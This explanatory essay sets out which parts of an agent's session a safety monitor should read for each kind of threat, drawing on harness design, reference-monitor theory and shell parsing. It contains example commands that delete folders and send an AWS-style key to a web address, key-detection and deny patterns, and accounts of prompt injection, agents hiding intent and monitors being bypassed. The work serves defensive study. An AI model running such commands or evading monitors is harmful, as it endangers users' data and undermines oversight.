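# What an AI Agent Monitor Should Inspect for Each Kind of Threat

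## What does an agent monitor read, and why should the threat decide?

An AI agent is a language model that acts by calling tools, such as a shell (the program that runs typed commands), a browser or an email client. An agent monitor is a check that reads some of what the agent does and allows, blocks or flags it. Some monitors are fixed rules a line or two long, and others are language models. Agents usually run with their user's privileges, so a bad command from an agent does as much damage as one from the user. Asking the user to approve every step is a weak defence. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users of Claude Code, the company's coding agent, accept 93% of permission prompts.

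A monitor's scope is the content it reads when it makes a decision. A rule can work well on one scope and fail completely on another, and the right scope depends on the harm the rule is meant to stop.

### How an agent works

A language model only produces text. The program around it, called the harness, turns some of that text into action. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes this cycle in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness builds a prompt from standing instructions, a list of available tools and the user's message, and sends it to the model. The model returns either a final message for the user or a tool call, which is a request to run one tool with given arguments. After a tool call, the harness runs the tool, appends the result to the prompt and queries the model again. The cycle repeats until the model returns a final message, which can take hundreds of tool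 calls.

In Bolin's example, a user asks for an architecture diagram in a project's README file. The model replies with two items. The first is its reasoning, which has a short readable summary and an encrypted remainder, and the second is a tool call to print the file in the shell. The harness runs the command and adds a third item containing the file's text. Each item has a type label, so a monitor can read one type and skip the rest.

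*Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (Joshi, 2026) catalogues design decisions, drawn largely from Joshi's own harness. It treats the model's reply as a request and lets the harness decide whether to act on it. A monitor that blocks tool calls works between the request and that decision.

### Where a monitor can read

There are six places to look.

- User messages hold what the person asked for, and so what the person authorised.
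- The agent's reasoning is the text the model produces before it acts. Some providers return it encrypted or only in summary.
- Tool calls hold the name of the tool and its full arguments, before anything has run.
- Tool results hold file contents, web pages and command output. Strangers wrote much of this text.
- Operating system events cover the programs, files and connections that the agent's processes open, including processes that its scripts start.
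- Network traffic shows which hosts those processes contact and, where the monitor can decrypt it, what they send.

The harness already handles the messages, reasoning, calls and results, so a check can attach there. Anthropic's *Hooks reference* documents points in Claude Code where a check can run: when the user submits a prompt, before a tool call (where the check can still block it) and after a call succeeds. A check on results comes too late to stop the action that produced them, but it can still affect the next action. For example, Claude Code's auto mode scans each result before the agent reads it and adds a warning if the text looks like an attempt to hijack the agent.

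Recording operating system events and network traffic requires instruments outside the harness, and it captures activity the harness never logs. *AgentSpy* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) ran agents inside a virtual machine and recorded their system calls, the requests that programs make to the operating system. When an agent had to find fabricated entries in a bibliography, its log showed a single piece of inline code, while the system calls showed 35 connections to the citation database Crossref to look up seven titles. The researchers also built a malicious version of the task's guidance files. In that run, the agent's log showed one script call that finished normally, but the system calls showed a program opening the user's private login key and then connecting to an outside host.

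Monitoring system calls also has gaps. The security rules in *AgentSpy* check which file a process opens or which host it contacts, one system call at a time, but a system call doesn't show whether the user wanted that action.

### The parts of a tool call, and two ways to be wrong

A single tool call mixes different kinds of content. Its executable part is whatever will run as instructions. Its payload is the data it carries, such as a message body or an uploaded file. Its destination is where it sends that data, including who can read it there. A threat class is a group of harms that leave the same kind of evidence. Deletions and leaked passwords belong to different classes because a deletion shows up in the executable part of a command and a leaked password in a payload.

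A monitor's false positive rate is the share of harmless actions that it blocks or flags, and its false negative rate is the share of harmful actions that it lets through. Lowering one tends to raise the other. The model that reviews actions in auto mode works in two stages, a fast filter and then a slower review of whatever the filter flags. On 10,000 real tool calls by its own staff, Anthropic measured a false positive rate of 8.5% for the filter alone and 0.4% for both stages together. But adding the second stage also raised the false negative rate, from 6.6% to 17% on 52 real cases of agents overstepping their instructions, and from 1.8% to 5.7% on 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out. A single overall error rate would have hidden the difference between these two results, although the test sets differ too much for a clean comparison between threats.

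### Four commands and two rules

A small example shows why scope matters so much. Take four shell commands:

```
A   git commit -m "Stop using rm -rf in the cleanup script"
B   rm -rf build
C   curl --data "key=AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE" https://example.com/report
D   curl --data "status=finished" https://example.com/report
```

Command A saves a change to a project's history, with a descriptive note that mentions a recursive delete (a command that removes a folder and everything in it). Command B deletes a folder. Commands C and D both send data to a web address. D's data is harmless, but C's contains an API key, a string that identifies a program to an online service much as a username does. The key is a dummy from the documentation of AWS, Amazon's cloud business. In this example, the user wants neither the deletion nor the key to go through.

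The monitor has two rules. The delete rule matches the characters `rm -rf`, as a sample script in the *Hooks reference* does. The key rule matches `AKIA` followed by sixteen capital letters or digits. That pattern comes from Debian's *gitleaks.toml*, a file of rules for finding leaked credentials. Trellix's *Amazon Web Services Keys* gives the same pattern for a data loss prevention product, which detects sensitive data leaving an organisation and stops it.

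Run both rules over the full text of each command, then again after deleting everything inside quotation marks:

| Command | Right answer | Whole text | Quoted strings removed |
|---|---|---|---|
| A: commit that mentions a delete | allow | block (false alarm) | allow |
| B: real delete | block | block | block |
| C: request carrying a key | block | block | allow (miss) |
| D: request carrying harmless data | allow | allow | allow |

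Removing the quotes fixes the false alarm on A, a kind that users of real agents have reported, but it causes the miss on C. Combining the two readings doesn't fix both errors. If a match in either reading is enough to block, A is a false alarm again, and if both readings must match, C still gets through. All four answers are right only when the delete rule checks the text without quotes and the key rule checks the text with them.

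The quoted text in A and C is data, which the shell doesn't run. That makes it irrelevant to the delete rule, but it is exactly what the key rule is meant to check.

Deleting quoted strings is a crude way to isolate the executable part of a command, because some programs run a quoted argument as code. Anthropic's sample includes a better method, an optional filter that splits a command into subcommands and runs the script only if one of them is an `rm` command. Command A has no `rm` subcommand, so the script wouldn't run on it. But when the script does run, it searches the full text of the command, so it would still raise a false alarm if A were joined to a command that harmlessly deletes a single file.

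Semgrep, a code scanner, publishes a rule that skips keys containing the word "example", so that rule would allow C on any scope.

### Matching scope to threat

The thesis, then, is that the threat class should decide what a monitor reads. Five classes cover most of what agent monitors are for.

Destructive commands delete or overwrite things that the user cannot easily get back. The evidence is in the executable part.

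To detect data leaks, a monitor should inspect the payload and the destination together. Bühler and colleagues recount a case that OpenAI disclosed in 2026, in which an agent uploaded data to a public paste site without authorisation, just to obtain a web address it could cite. Searching for key-shaped strings is unsuitable for such a case, because the upload was a leak due to who could read the site. Other leaks are visible only in the path that data took through the session. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) separates two controls for this reason. A sandbox uses the operating system or a virtual machine to limit what the agent's processes can reach, which determines whether the agent can access the data at all. Information-flow control labels data by secrecy and trustworthiness, keeps those labels attached as the agent uses the data, and checks them before each action.

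Prompt injection diverts an agent from the user's task through instructions hidden in content the agent reads. These instructions arrive through tool results, and auto mode's warning system scans those results for them.

An overeager action is meant to help the user but goes beyond what the user authorised. Anthropic describes a user who asked an agent to "clean up old branches", the parallel lines of work in a project. The agent issued a command to delete branches on the shared server, though the user may have meant only local copies. A monitor can tell from the command that the action is irreversible, but it needs the user's message to tell whether anyone asked for it.

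An agent with concealed intent pursues an aim that its visible actions do not reveal, so its reasoning may be the only place to find that aim. OpenAI's *Detecting misbehavior in frontier reasoning models* (2025) reports that a model reading other models' reasoning caught them subverting tests in coding tasks. It also reports that penalising the incriminating thoughts left most of the misbehaviour in place and taught the models to hide their intent, so developers can destroy this evidence by training against it.

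The classes overlap, as the deleted branches show. Anthropic instead sorts dangers by cause (overeagerness, honest mistakes, prompt injection and a misaligned model) and observes that blocking the action works whatever the cause. This is a fair challenge to the need to sort threats at all. Yet in Anthropic's own design, the injection check reads tool results, while the reviewer of actions reads user messages and tool calls. In most of the reviewer's misses that Anthropic examined, it had recognised the dangerous command but misjudged whether the user had consented, which is a separate question that requires different evidence. The reviewer had access to the user's messages in these cases, so reading the right material does not guarantee a correct judgement.

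The threat may not be the only factor that determines what a monitor should read. Joshi argues from design experience that, even for shell commands alone, approving a command requires an exact reading and refusing one requires a broad reading, and that "one reading cannot do both". Joshi reports that their own harness does not yet meet the rule that follows from this argument.

### Why not let a capable model read everything?

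The best reply to the thesis is that only weak monitors need separate scopes. A capable language model can tell a commit message from a command, which a pattern cannot do. If it reads the whole session, it will recognize that the `rm -rf` in A is a note and that the string in C is a key being sent out, so no one has to decide in advance which text each rule gets.

The four commands support this reply more than they might seem to. Removing the quoted strings makes C and D identical, so no monitor could tell them apart, however capable. A better monitor can tell A from B if it reads the full text. So a better monitor can't recover evidence that was removed, but it may avoid the false alarms that come from reading too much.

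Some published work partly supports this approach. *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction for Attack Detection in Agentic Systems* (2026) uses a single model to audit for unauthorised operations, data leaks and high-risk commands. For cases like A, it instructs the model not to flag routine work such as commits. OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025) states that monitoring a model's reasoning can be far more effective than monitoring its actions and outputs alone. That supports reading more than the tool calls, but it doesn't show that one reader should have everything.

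Whether the reply succeeds depends on how much the extra text hinders a capable reader. Some evidence suggests that it reduces accuracy. When Anthropic also gave its reviewer the agent's own messages and the tool results, the reviewer got worse at catching overeager actions. The reviewer was Claude Sonnet 4.6, and a stronger model might lose less accuracy.

The security risk looks harder to remove. An attacker's text enters a session through tool results, so a monitor that reads them is exposed to the same text that may have hijacked the agent. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* conjectures that persistent attackers will always get past defences that rely on a model to separate instructions from data. The conjecture mainly concerns the agent's model, but the same concern applies to a monitor built on a model. It is unproven, and better models may resist such text for longer, but it gives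 designers a reason to keep hostile text away from any monitor that doesn't need to read it.

Giving a monitor "everything" also tends to mean giving it only what the harness logged. In the bibliography task with the malicious guidance files, a model reading the complete log would have seen one script call that finished normally and nothing about the private key.

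## What can a monitor enforce, given what it can see?

The information a monitor reads strictly limits what it can stop. Most of the theory behind this limit predates AI agents and comes from research on operating systems and military secrecy.

### The reference monitor

In the early 1970s, the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Guards and locked rooms keep outsiders out, but they don't stop a malicious user with a legitimate account. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) proposed checking every access that such a user's programs make.

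A reference monitor stands between subjects (users and the programs that act for them) and objects (files, devices and other programs), and checks each access against a table. The table has a row for each subject and a column for each object, and each cell lists the permitted kinds of access, such as read, write or execute. An agent, whatever its intentions, is in much the same position as Anderson's malicious user, because it works under a legitimate account on the system.

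Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism that does the checking:

- It must be tamper-proof.
- It must always be invoked, so that no access goes around it.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

These requirements are harder to meet than they sound. Anderson applied them to the Honeywell HIS 635 computer and its operating system, GCOS III. The hardware confined each program to its own region of memory, which made it a kind of reference monitor. But programs had to call the operating system for input and output, and most of the operating system ran with that confinement switched off, so the check was not always invoked. The operating system itself would not have met the requirements either. With its supporting software, it had 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many to test completely, and several teams of testers had already broken into it.

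Agent monitors have the same problem. If a tool call can start a script, a check on tool calls is not always invoked, because the script opens files and connections without going through the harness. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* allows the monitor to consist of several enforcement points, such as a gateway for tools and a proxy for outgoing traffic, as long as together they check every security-relevant action before it happens.

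A monitor built on a language model fails the third requirement. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) points out that nobody can prove such a model will always apply its policy. It gives the hypothetical example of a model that correctly refuses 99% of unauthorised requests, which leaves an attacker the other 1%. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, an attacker who made 100 attempts would have a 63% chance of getting at least one through.

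The idea that a monitor's design should start from the threat has a long history. Anderson's procedure for building a secure system begins by defining the threats the system must withstand, and the monitor's design follows from them. Anderson's table includes no control over what a program does with data it has permission to read.

### Safety properties

Even a perfect reference monitor can't enforce every policy. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* identifies which policies a mechanism can enforce by watching a program step by step and halting it when the next step would break the rules. Firewalls, operating system kernels, and monitors that block an agent's tool calls all work this way.

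Schneider treats a run of a program, called an execution, as a finite or infinite sequence of steps. A monitor that watches one execution works under three constraints. It sees only the run in front of it, so the policy has to judge each execution by itself. It can't see the future, and the program might stop at any moment, so a partial run that breaks the policy must stay in breach however it continues. And it has to reject a bad run after a finite number of steps. Policies that meet all three conditions are safety properties, which informally means that some "bad thing" never happens. Formally, a set G of acceptable executions is a safety property if:

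```
for every execution s outside G there is a number i such that
no execution beginning with the first i steps of s is in G
```

In other words, every bad run has a point of no return, and the monitor must act before the program passes it.

Schneider's example is a rule against sending messages after reading a file. The monitor needs two states. It starts in "no file read", where it permits every step. A file read moves it to "file read", where it permits every step except a send. If an agent lists a folder, reads a customer file and then tries to make a web request, the monitor halts it before anything leaves the machine.

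By contrast, the rule "the agent must eventually tell the user about each deletion" is not a safety property, because the agent could always report the deletion later. Adding a deadline, as in "report each deletion before running the next command", makes it a safety property, because a later report can't undo the violation. Schneider makes the same change to a rule that nobody may be denied a resource forever. A maximum wait in seconds is a safety property, but a monitor that works by halting the program can't enforce it, because time keeps passing after the program stops. Such a monitor can enforce a maximum wait counted in program steps.

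The restriction to safety properties applies to monitors that can only halt the run. Fong (2004), in *Access Control By Tracking Shallow Execution History*, credits Bauer, Ligatti and Walker with showing that monitors that can also suppress or insert steps can enforce more properties. A monitor that can insert steps could send the missing deletion report itself.

Any rule of this kind depends on how completely its author has defined the events. Schneider warns that a system may have many ways to send a message, some buried deep inside it, and that the definition of "send" has to include them all. For an agent, these include web requests, emails, browser forms and anything its scripts send. In the bibliography task that Bühler and colleagues ran, a monitor reading only the agent's log would have counted no sends.

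If several monitors each enforce a safety policy and each can halt the program, running them side by side enforces all of the policies. Schneider recommends splitting policies up like this, because people find one huge policy hard to understand and because each small policy can then have its own mechanism, placed wherever its events occur. This justifies giving the delete rule and the key rule different text to read. However, any one of the monitors can also stop harmless work, so adding a monitor may increase false alarms and cannot reduce them.

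### Secrecy depends on runs that did not happen

Data leaks are the awkward case, because secrecy is not a safety property. It isn't a property of single executions at all.

The standard definition of secrecy comes from Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*. One group of users is noninterfering with another if nothing the first group does has any effect on what the second group sees. To test this, take any sequence of commands, delete the first group's commands from it, and compare what a member of the second group sees in each case:

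```
output to u after w  =  output to u after w with group G's commands deleted
```

The equation must hold for every command sequence w and every user u in the second group. In a military system, users with high clearance must not interfere with users with lower clearance. The definition is strict. Suppose a file doesn't exist at the start, and the commands that create, change or delete it must not interfere with some user. The system must then report to that user that the file doesn't exist, whatever anyone has done with it.

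The equation compares two runs, but a monitor sees only one of them. Command D from the earlier example posts `status=finished` to a web address, and the run looks the same whether or not those words disclose anything about the customer file. They disclose that a certain customer is in debt if the agent would have posted something else had that customer not been in debt. They reveal nothing about the file if the agent would have posted them whatever the file contained.

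*Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) builds a general theory around this difference. A trace is a recorded execution. A trace property is a set of traces, and a system satisfies it if every trace the system can produce belongs to the set. "No network write after a file read" is a trace property. A hyperproperty is a set of sets of traces, and a system satisfies it if the complete set of traces the system can produce is one of the members. Noninterference is a hyperproperty, because whether one trace is acceptable depends on which other traces are possible.

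Their smallest example is a system that unpredictably outputs 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. Both 0 and 1 are possible outputs whatever the secret is, so the set of possible outputs doesn't depend on it. If the system is restricted to always output the secret bit, every remaining run was already possible in the original system, but the output now reveals the secret. Removing runs can therefore break secrecy, although it can never break a safety property. So a monitor could, in principle, make a system leakier by blocking some of its harmless outputs.

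Goguen and Meseguer assumed a deterministic machine, but the language model in an agent picks its words partly at random, so two runs of the same request can differ even when the secrets are the same. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, therefore compare the probabilities of public outcomes. They designed a small programming language for agents and proved that, in any program written in it, changing the secrets does not change how likely each public outcome is, apart from what an observer could learn from whether the program finishes. The proof covers agents that write and run their own code, and the proof checker Lean has verified it.

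This is consistent with Schneider's footnote that monitors said to prevent information flow actually enforce a stricter policy that implies secrecy. The rule against sending after reading a file is one such policy. It prevents leaks from files by blocking every later message, including a harmless `status=finished`. Forbidding every run would also guarantee secrecy, but the agent could do nothing. Labels that travel with data are a more practical approximation, though they also block some harmless actions.

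An approximation can also be too loose. Garby and colleagues found a gap in CaMeL, an earlier agent defence that labels data by its source. A program can reveal a secret by skipping a step as well as by taking one, but CaMeL raises labels only on steps that run. The gap arises because CaMeL watches a single execution, and the evidence is in the branch the program didn't take.

### How much history the monitor keeps

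Schneider's monitor may remember everything that has happened so far. Real ones remember less, and many rules for agents look at one tool call and then forget it. Fong sorted monitors by what they remember, and the main classes are these (the sample rules are illustrations for agents):

| Class | What the monitor remembers | A rule it can enforce |
|---|---|---|
| Memoryless | nothing | never delete the home folder |
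| Shallow history | which events have occurred, but not their order | no web requests once the agent has read a private file |
| Stack | which calls are still in progress | no web requests while a downloaded script is running |
| Full history | every event, in order | no deployment unless the tests ran after the last edit |

Fong shows that a monitor needs only shallow history to enforce several well-known security policies. One is the Chinese Wall, which keeps a consultant who has seen one company's data away from its competitors' data. Another classifies programs by their behaviour, so a program that opens a network connection is treated as a browser from then on and can no longer read the user's files. This rule would apply to an agent almost unchanged.

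A monitor with shallow history cannot enforce the deployment rule, because it records which actions an agent has taken but not their order. Suppose one agent edits the code, runs the tests and deploys, which is allowed. Another runs the tests, edits the code and deploys, which is not. Just before deployment, the monitor's record for both agents shows that an edit and a test have occurred. It therefore either blocks the first agent wrongly or lets the second deploy untested changes.

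Fong proved that this ordering is general. A monitor whose record distinguishes every pair of histories that another's does, and some further pairs, can enforce every policy the other can and some that it can't. But some records can't be ranked this way. A monitor that keeps only a stack can't enforce the shallow-history rule in the table, because a file read leaves the stack as soon as it finishes. A monitor that keeps only a shallow history can't enforce the stack rule, because once the history contains the start and end of a script, starting the script again doesn't change it.

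A monitor that keeps only a set of events can enforce the deployment rule if it erases "tests ran" from the set at each new edit. Erasing the entry doesn't mean the monitor works with less information, because the set now shows whether tests have run since the last edit. A set that only accumulates events loses that order.

Fong cautions that these comparisons hold only if the monitors receive the same events. If each event includes the time it happened, a monitor with a shallow history can enforce everything that one with a full history can. A monitor's scope therefore depends on both how far back its record goes and how much each entry shows. A monitor with a complete history of tool names but not their arguments would still miss a key in a payload.

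### An error bound

The two deployments illustrate a simple limit. If a harmful session and a harmless one look identical to the monitor, it must give both the same answer, so it gets one of them wrong. A probabilistic version of this limit covers sessions that look similar but not identical.

Let P(v) be the probability that a harmful session shows the monitor the view v, and let Q(v) be the same probability for a harmless session. Any monitor, however clever, amounts to a function b(v), the probability that it blocks when it sees v. Summing over all views gives its error rates:

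```
false positive rate  =  sum of Q(v) b(v)
false negative rate  =  sum of P(v) (1 - b(v))

their total          =  1 - sum of (P(v) - Q(v)) b(v)
```

The total is smallest when the last sum is largest. That happens when the monitor blocks every view that is likelier in harmful sessions and allows all the others. The sum then equals the total variation distance between P and Q. This is a number from 0 to 1, the largest gap between the probabilities that P and Q give to any one set of views. It is 0 when the two distributions are the same and 1 when they never overlap. Therefore:

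```
false positive rate + false negative rate  >=  1 - TV(P, Q)
```

An agent that uploads a customer list may be sending it to the team's private folder, which is fine, or to a public paste site, which is a leak. If the monitor sees the file but not the destination, the two uploads look the same to it and the distance between them is 0. Blocking both gives a false positive rate of 100%, and allowing both gives a false negative rate of 100%. Blocking at random three times in ten gives a false positive rate of 30% and a false negative rate of 70%. The two rates always add up to 100%, however smart the monitor is.

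Mixed traffic is more realistic. Suppose that every harmful upload sends customer data to a public site. Of the harmless uploads, 40% send customer data to the private folder, 30% send ordinary files to a public site, and 30% send ordinary files to the private folder. Then the best possible totals are:

| What the monitor sees | Distance | Lowest possible total of the two rates |
|---|---|---|
| Only that an upload took place | 0 | 100% |
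| Whether the payload is customer data | 0.6 | 40% |
| Whether the destination is public | 0.7 | 30% |
| Payload and destination | 1 | 0% |

A monitor can separate the cases completely by using the payload and the destination together, but not by using either alone. These percentages are invented, and the cases would overlap more in real traffic.

A monitor with a limited view also does much worse in practice than the bound suggests. A monitor that sees only the payload reaches its 40% total by blocking every upload of customer data, including 40% of all harmless uploads. No team would accept that. If the team tolerates a false positive rate of 1%, the monitor can block only one in forty of the uploads that contain customer data, so it misses 97.5% of the leaks. Deployed monitors have to keep their false positive rates low because harmless actions usually far outnumber harmful ones.

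The inequality also gives a lower bound on how much information a monitor's view contains, based on the monitor's measured errors. For the fast filter in Claude Code's auto mode, the two error rates on real actions add up to 15.1% (8.5% plus 6.6%), so the distance between harmful and harmless actions in the filter's view was at least about 0.85 on Anthropic's test sets. That figure is rough because there were only 52 harmful cases, but it rules out a nearly worthless view.

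All of this depends on P, which depends on the threat. When a monitor reads the four shell commands without their quoted strings, the distance between the delete and the harmless commands is 1, but the distance between the two web requests is 0. A scope is therefore good or bad only relative to a class of harms, and this part of the thesis follows from arithmetic.

### Can a wider view do harm?

The bound gives a reason to show the monitor enough. It gives no reason to hold anything back.

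Suppose a fixed procedure turns a wide view into a narrow one, for example by deleting quoted strings or dropping tool results. A monitor with the wide view can run that procedure itself, apply the best rule for the narrow view, and get the same error rates. So its lowest total error can't be higher than the narrow monitor's, and the distance between P and Q can't be smaller in the wide view than in the narrow one. In information theory, this is called the data-processing inequality, which says that processing data can't make two sources easier to tell apart. Fong makes a similar point about which policies are enforceable by ordering monitors by their records.

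The argument still holds when an attacker writes part of the text. A monitor with the wide view can ignore that part and apply the narrow monitor's rule, so its worst case is no worse than the narrow monitor's.

The analysis above assumes an ideal monitor, one that always applies the best available rule and costs nothing to run. The threat determines the least such a monitor must read, but reading more never makes it worse. If a real monitor does better when it reads less, then either it failed to use a better rule that was already available, or that rule cost too much to use. The benefit of narrowing what a monitor reads therefore has three possible sources.

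A monitor may be distracted by other text even when it can see the evidence it needs. The delete rule raised a false alarm on the commit note, although the quotation marks showing that the alarm was false were visible. Anthropic's reviewer became less accurate when it read more of the session, although it could have ignored the extra text. Learning from examples makes this problem worse, because sessions can take more forms when the monitor sees more of them, and any set of examples then covers those forms more sparsely.

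Monitors can also be manipulated. Christodorescu and colleagues note that attackers can search systematically for inputs that look benign to a language model but lead it to break its policy. An ideal monitor would ignore such text, but a real one needs to be shielded from it by limiting what it reads. This protection is incomplete because a hijacked agent also writes its tool calls under the attacker's influence, so the calls themselves can carry manipulative text. Nor can the monitor be shielded when the hostile text is the evidence it needs to inspect, as with prompt injection.

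Schneider observes that a monitor whose policy refers to any part of a program's state may have to intervene at every machine instruction. A filter can reduce this overhead by forwarding only the events that would change the monitor's own state, without limiting the monitor's ability to enforce the policy. But a program that can corrupt the filter can get around the monitor. The same is true when an agent's harness trims a transcript before a reviewer reads it. The trimming code is part of the monitor, so Anderson's three requirements apply to it as well.

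## What must a monitor read to catch a harmful command?

A monitor can detect a destructive command in the executable part of a tool call, so it first has to find that part. This is easy for many tools. A file-editing tool, for example, has separate fields for the path and the new text, and nothing in the text field runs. It is harder for the shell tool, which has a single field that mixes the program, its options and any text the command contains.

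### How a shell turns text into actions

Bash, a widely used shell, handles a line in roughly four steps:

1. It splits the line into words and operators. Quotation marks hold text together as one word, even if the text contains spaces.
2. It groups the words into commands. Operators such as `&&`, `;` and `|` end one command and begin another.
3. It expands the words. It replaces variables with their values and wildcards with matching file names. It also replaces a command substitution (a command written inside another command) with that command's output, which means running it first.
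4. It opens any files that the line reads from or writes to, then runs each command. The first word names the program and the others are its arguments.

In command A from the earlier example, `git commit -m "Stop using rm -rf in the cleanup script"`, the first step turns the whole commit message into one word, which Git receives as an argument and saves. In command B, `rm -rf build`, `rm` comes first, so the shell runs it.

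Quoted text isn't always inert, because Bash still expands variables and runs command substitutions inside double quotes, though not inside single quotes. *QuoteBench* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a test of how reliably models write shell commands, includes a task where the obvious answer fails for this reason. The model must save some text that contains the word `date` between backticks, an old notation for command substitution. If the model puts the text in double quotes, Bash runs the `date` program and saves its output in place of the word. The same accident could happen in a commit note, because people who write about code often put backticks around commands. If the agent put the deletion command in backticks inside a double-quoted note, Bash would delete the folder before git received the note.

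Whether text is executed can also depend on the program that receives it. Git stores a quoted argument, but an interpreter runs it as code. OpenAI's *Rules*, the documentation for command rules in Codex, gives the example of a call that starts Bash with the string `git add . && rm -rf /`. Bash receives the string as one argument, then parses it as shell code and finds two commands, the second of which deletes everything it can reach. A monitor therefore needs to know which programs are interpreters and which of their arguments they run.

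### Approving and refusing need different readings

Under Joshi's rule, approving a command requires an exact reading, while refusing one requires a broad reading. The rule follows from how hard these steps are to imitate. Suppose a user forbids `rm` but lets an agent run `npm test`, which tests a JavaScript project, without asking. A strict parser returns nothing for a command it can't fully parse. That is right for approvals, because approving a command based on a guess may let something else run. But it also leaves no program names to check against the ban on `rm`. A permissive parser lists every program that might run, which suits the ban but makes approvals unsafe.

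One of the designs Joshi describes uses both readings. In outline, it makes these checks in order:

```
refuse    if any command in the broad reading is forbidden
approve   if the strict reading succeeds and every command in it is allowed
ask       otherwise
```

A monitor that reads commands strictly has to interpret every character exactly as every supported shell would. Strict reading also produces more approval prompts for odd but harmless commands, and users who already approve almost every prompt may read the extra ones even less carefully.

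A monitor can use the shell's own parser to help it read commands exactly. *Look Before You Leap* (2026) combines Bash's syntax check with a test of whether the named program exists. On 9,930 commands, these two checks rejected no valid command and caught half of the invalid ones. The full system, which also compares options with each program's help pages, caught 95.8% of invalid commands but rejected 10% of valid ones. These checks only test whether a command is valid, so they can't identify valid commands that could do harm, such as `rm -rf build`.

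Claude Code applies deny rules more broadly than allow rules, according to Anthropic's permission documentation. It splits a compound command into subcommands and applies an allow rule only if every subcommand is allowed, but it applies a deny rule if any subcommand matches, including a nested one. Deny rules also still match a command that begins by setting an unfamiliar variable, while allow rules don't. When a file path goes through a symbolic link (a file that points to another file), an allow rule must match both the link and its target, but a deny rule needs to match only one of them. In manual mode, Claude Code asks the user about commands it can't fully parse and any command longer than 10,000 characters. However, Anthropic warns that a deny rule covers only the usual way of invoking a program and recommends a sandbox for restrictions that must hold.

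If a script contains only plain words and simple operators, Codex splits it into commands, checks each one and applies the most restrictive result. If the script uses more advanced features, Codex treats it as one call to Bash. This prevents an allow rule for `git add` from approving the rest of the script, but it also leaves a rule forbidding `rm` with no separate `rm` command to match, which is the problem Joshi describes. The consequences are limited because these rules decide what may run outside Codex's sandbox, and a command that matches no rule doesn't gain that permission from them.

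GitHub's *Bash Command Parser Specification* describes the parser used for permission decisions in its Copilot software development kit. The parser splits commands at operators outside quoted text, but GitHub states that it is not a full shell parser. A partial parser can still support safe approvals if it declines any syntax it doesn't cover.

The evidence for Joshi's rule is thin. It comes mainly from Joshi's own harness, which no second rater assessed. In the worked example, code written to find a command's name was later trusted to approve commands, and a review found inputs that the code and the shell parsed differently. Joshi also studied ten other harnesses, unnamed in the paper, and adopted some of their patterns. Claude Code's similar design may therefore be one of the rule's sources, so it can't count as independent confirmation.

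*CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that handles both approval and refusal, using more than one reading of each command. It gives each command a single risk score and sets two thresholds. Commands below the lower threshold run, commands above the upper one are refused, and most of those in between go to a language model. The system also keeps the original text alongside a cleaned-up version and searches both. If parsing fails and the text still contains strong signs of danger, it refuses the command.

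### Judging what a command would do

Parsing identifies the programs that will run, but the monitor still has to know what they do. Liu and colleagues measured how much each kind of knowledge adds by removing one layer of their system at a time. They used 220 dangerous commands and 329 safe ones, and switched off the language model:

| Version of the system | Dangerous commands caught | Safe commands blocked |
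|---|---|---|
| All layers | 75.9% | 1.8% |
| Without the syntax tree | 73.2% | 1.8% |
| Without knowledge of programs and options | 42.3% | 1.8% |
| Without checks on file paths | 52.7% | 1.5% |
| Without the list of known dangerous patterns | 60.9% | 0.3% |

Knowing what programs do and where they act helped the monitor most. The path check lets a command read `/etc/os-release`, which describes the operating system, but flags one that adds a line to `/etc/profile`, a startup script for every user. Removing the syntax tree hurt performance only slightly, but that may be because most of the safe commands in the test came from a public collection of everyday shell commands, which may contain few harmless notes that quote a deletion command.

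A set of 22 keyword rules caught only 17.3% of the dangerous commands, with no false alarms. An open coding model with 30 billion parameters, used as a judge, caught 67.3% but also blocked 11.3% of the safe commands. Much stronger models exist now, so this comparison is weak evidence of the best a model can do.

Taneja and Weber (2026), in *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action*, classify commands by consequence. Their resolver, a fixed set of rules with no language model, assigns each command to one of 33 classes. These include destructive commands, access to credentials, running code from the internet, and several kinds of file write. The classes have a severity order, and the resolver works as follows:

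```
class of a command  =  the most severe class whose rule matches it,
                       or "generic shell command" if no rule matches
```

Taking the most severe match is a broad reading in Joshi's sense, since a harmless first half of a command can't lower the class of a harmful second half. A command that matches no rule gets a default class, and the system holds it for the user's approval. After enough consecutive approvals for the same class on the same resource, the system stops asking for approval, unless the class is one of the thirteen most severe, for which it always asks.

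The rules match a dangerous argument only where it would take effect for a particular program. Taneja and Weber tightened this matching after three rounds of false alarms in the rule for detecting remote code execution. The old patterns allowed too much text between their parts, so a web address in ordinary prose and an install command hundreds of characters away could together trigger the rule.

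Taneja and Weber tested the system by having an agent install 53 skills, which are folders of written instructions for an agent to follow. The system held 148 commands for approval and blocked another 22. Taneja and Weber drew 50 of the held commands at random and judged that 49 were in the right class. But 145 of the 148 held commands were in the generic class, so the audit mostly confirms that the system classified ordinary commands correctly and is weak evidence of how well it classifies others.

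They also examined all three held commands that had a more specific class. Two did read a file of secrets. The third was a false alarm. The agent was writing a new file, and the resolver classed the command as destructive because the file's text contained a dangerous pattern. This is the same mistake as with command A, even though this system was designed to match by position. The resolver checks where an argument stands relative to a program's name, but it doesn't detect that the name is inside a block of text. Taneja and Weber had not fixed the fault when they published. They work for Pheo, the company that sells the system, and they audited it themselves.

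A second audit found the opposite problem with interpreters. Taneja and Weber ran the resolver over the written instructions of skills that a public registry's scanners had cleared, then checked 100 of the skills it flagged. They judged 92 of the flags correct. Five of the eight errors involved downloads that went to an interpreter only for formatting. The interpreter treated these downloads as data, so recognising the interpreter wasn't enough to show that anything from the internet would run as code.

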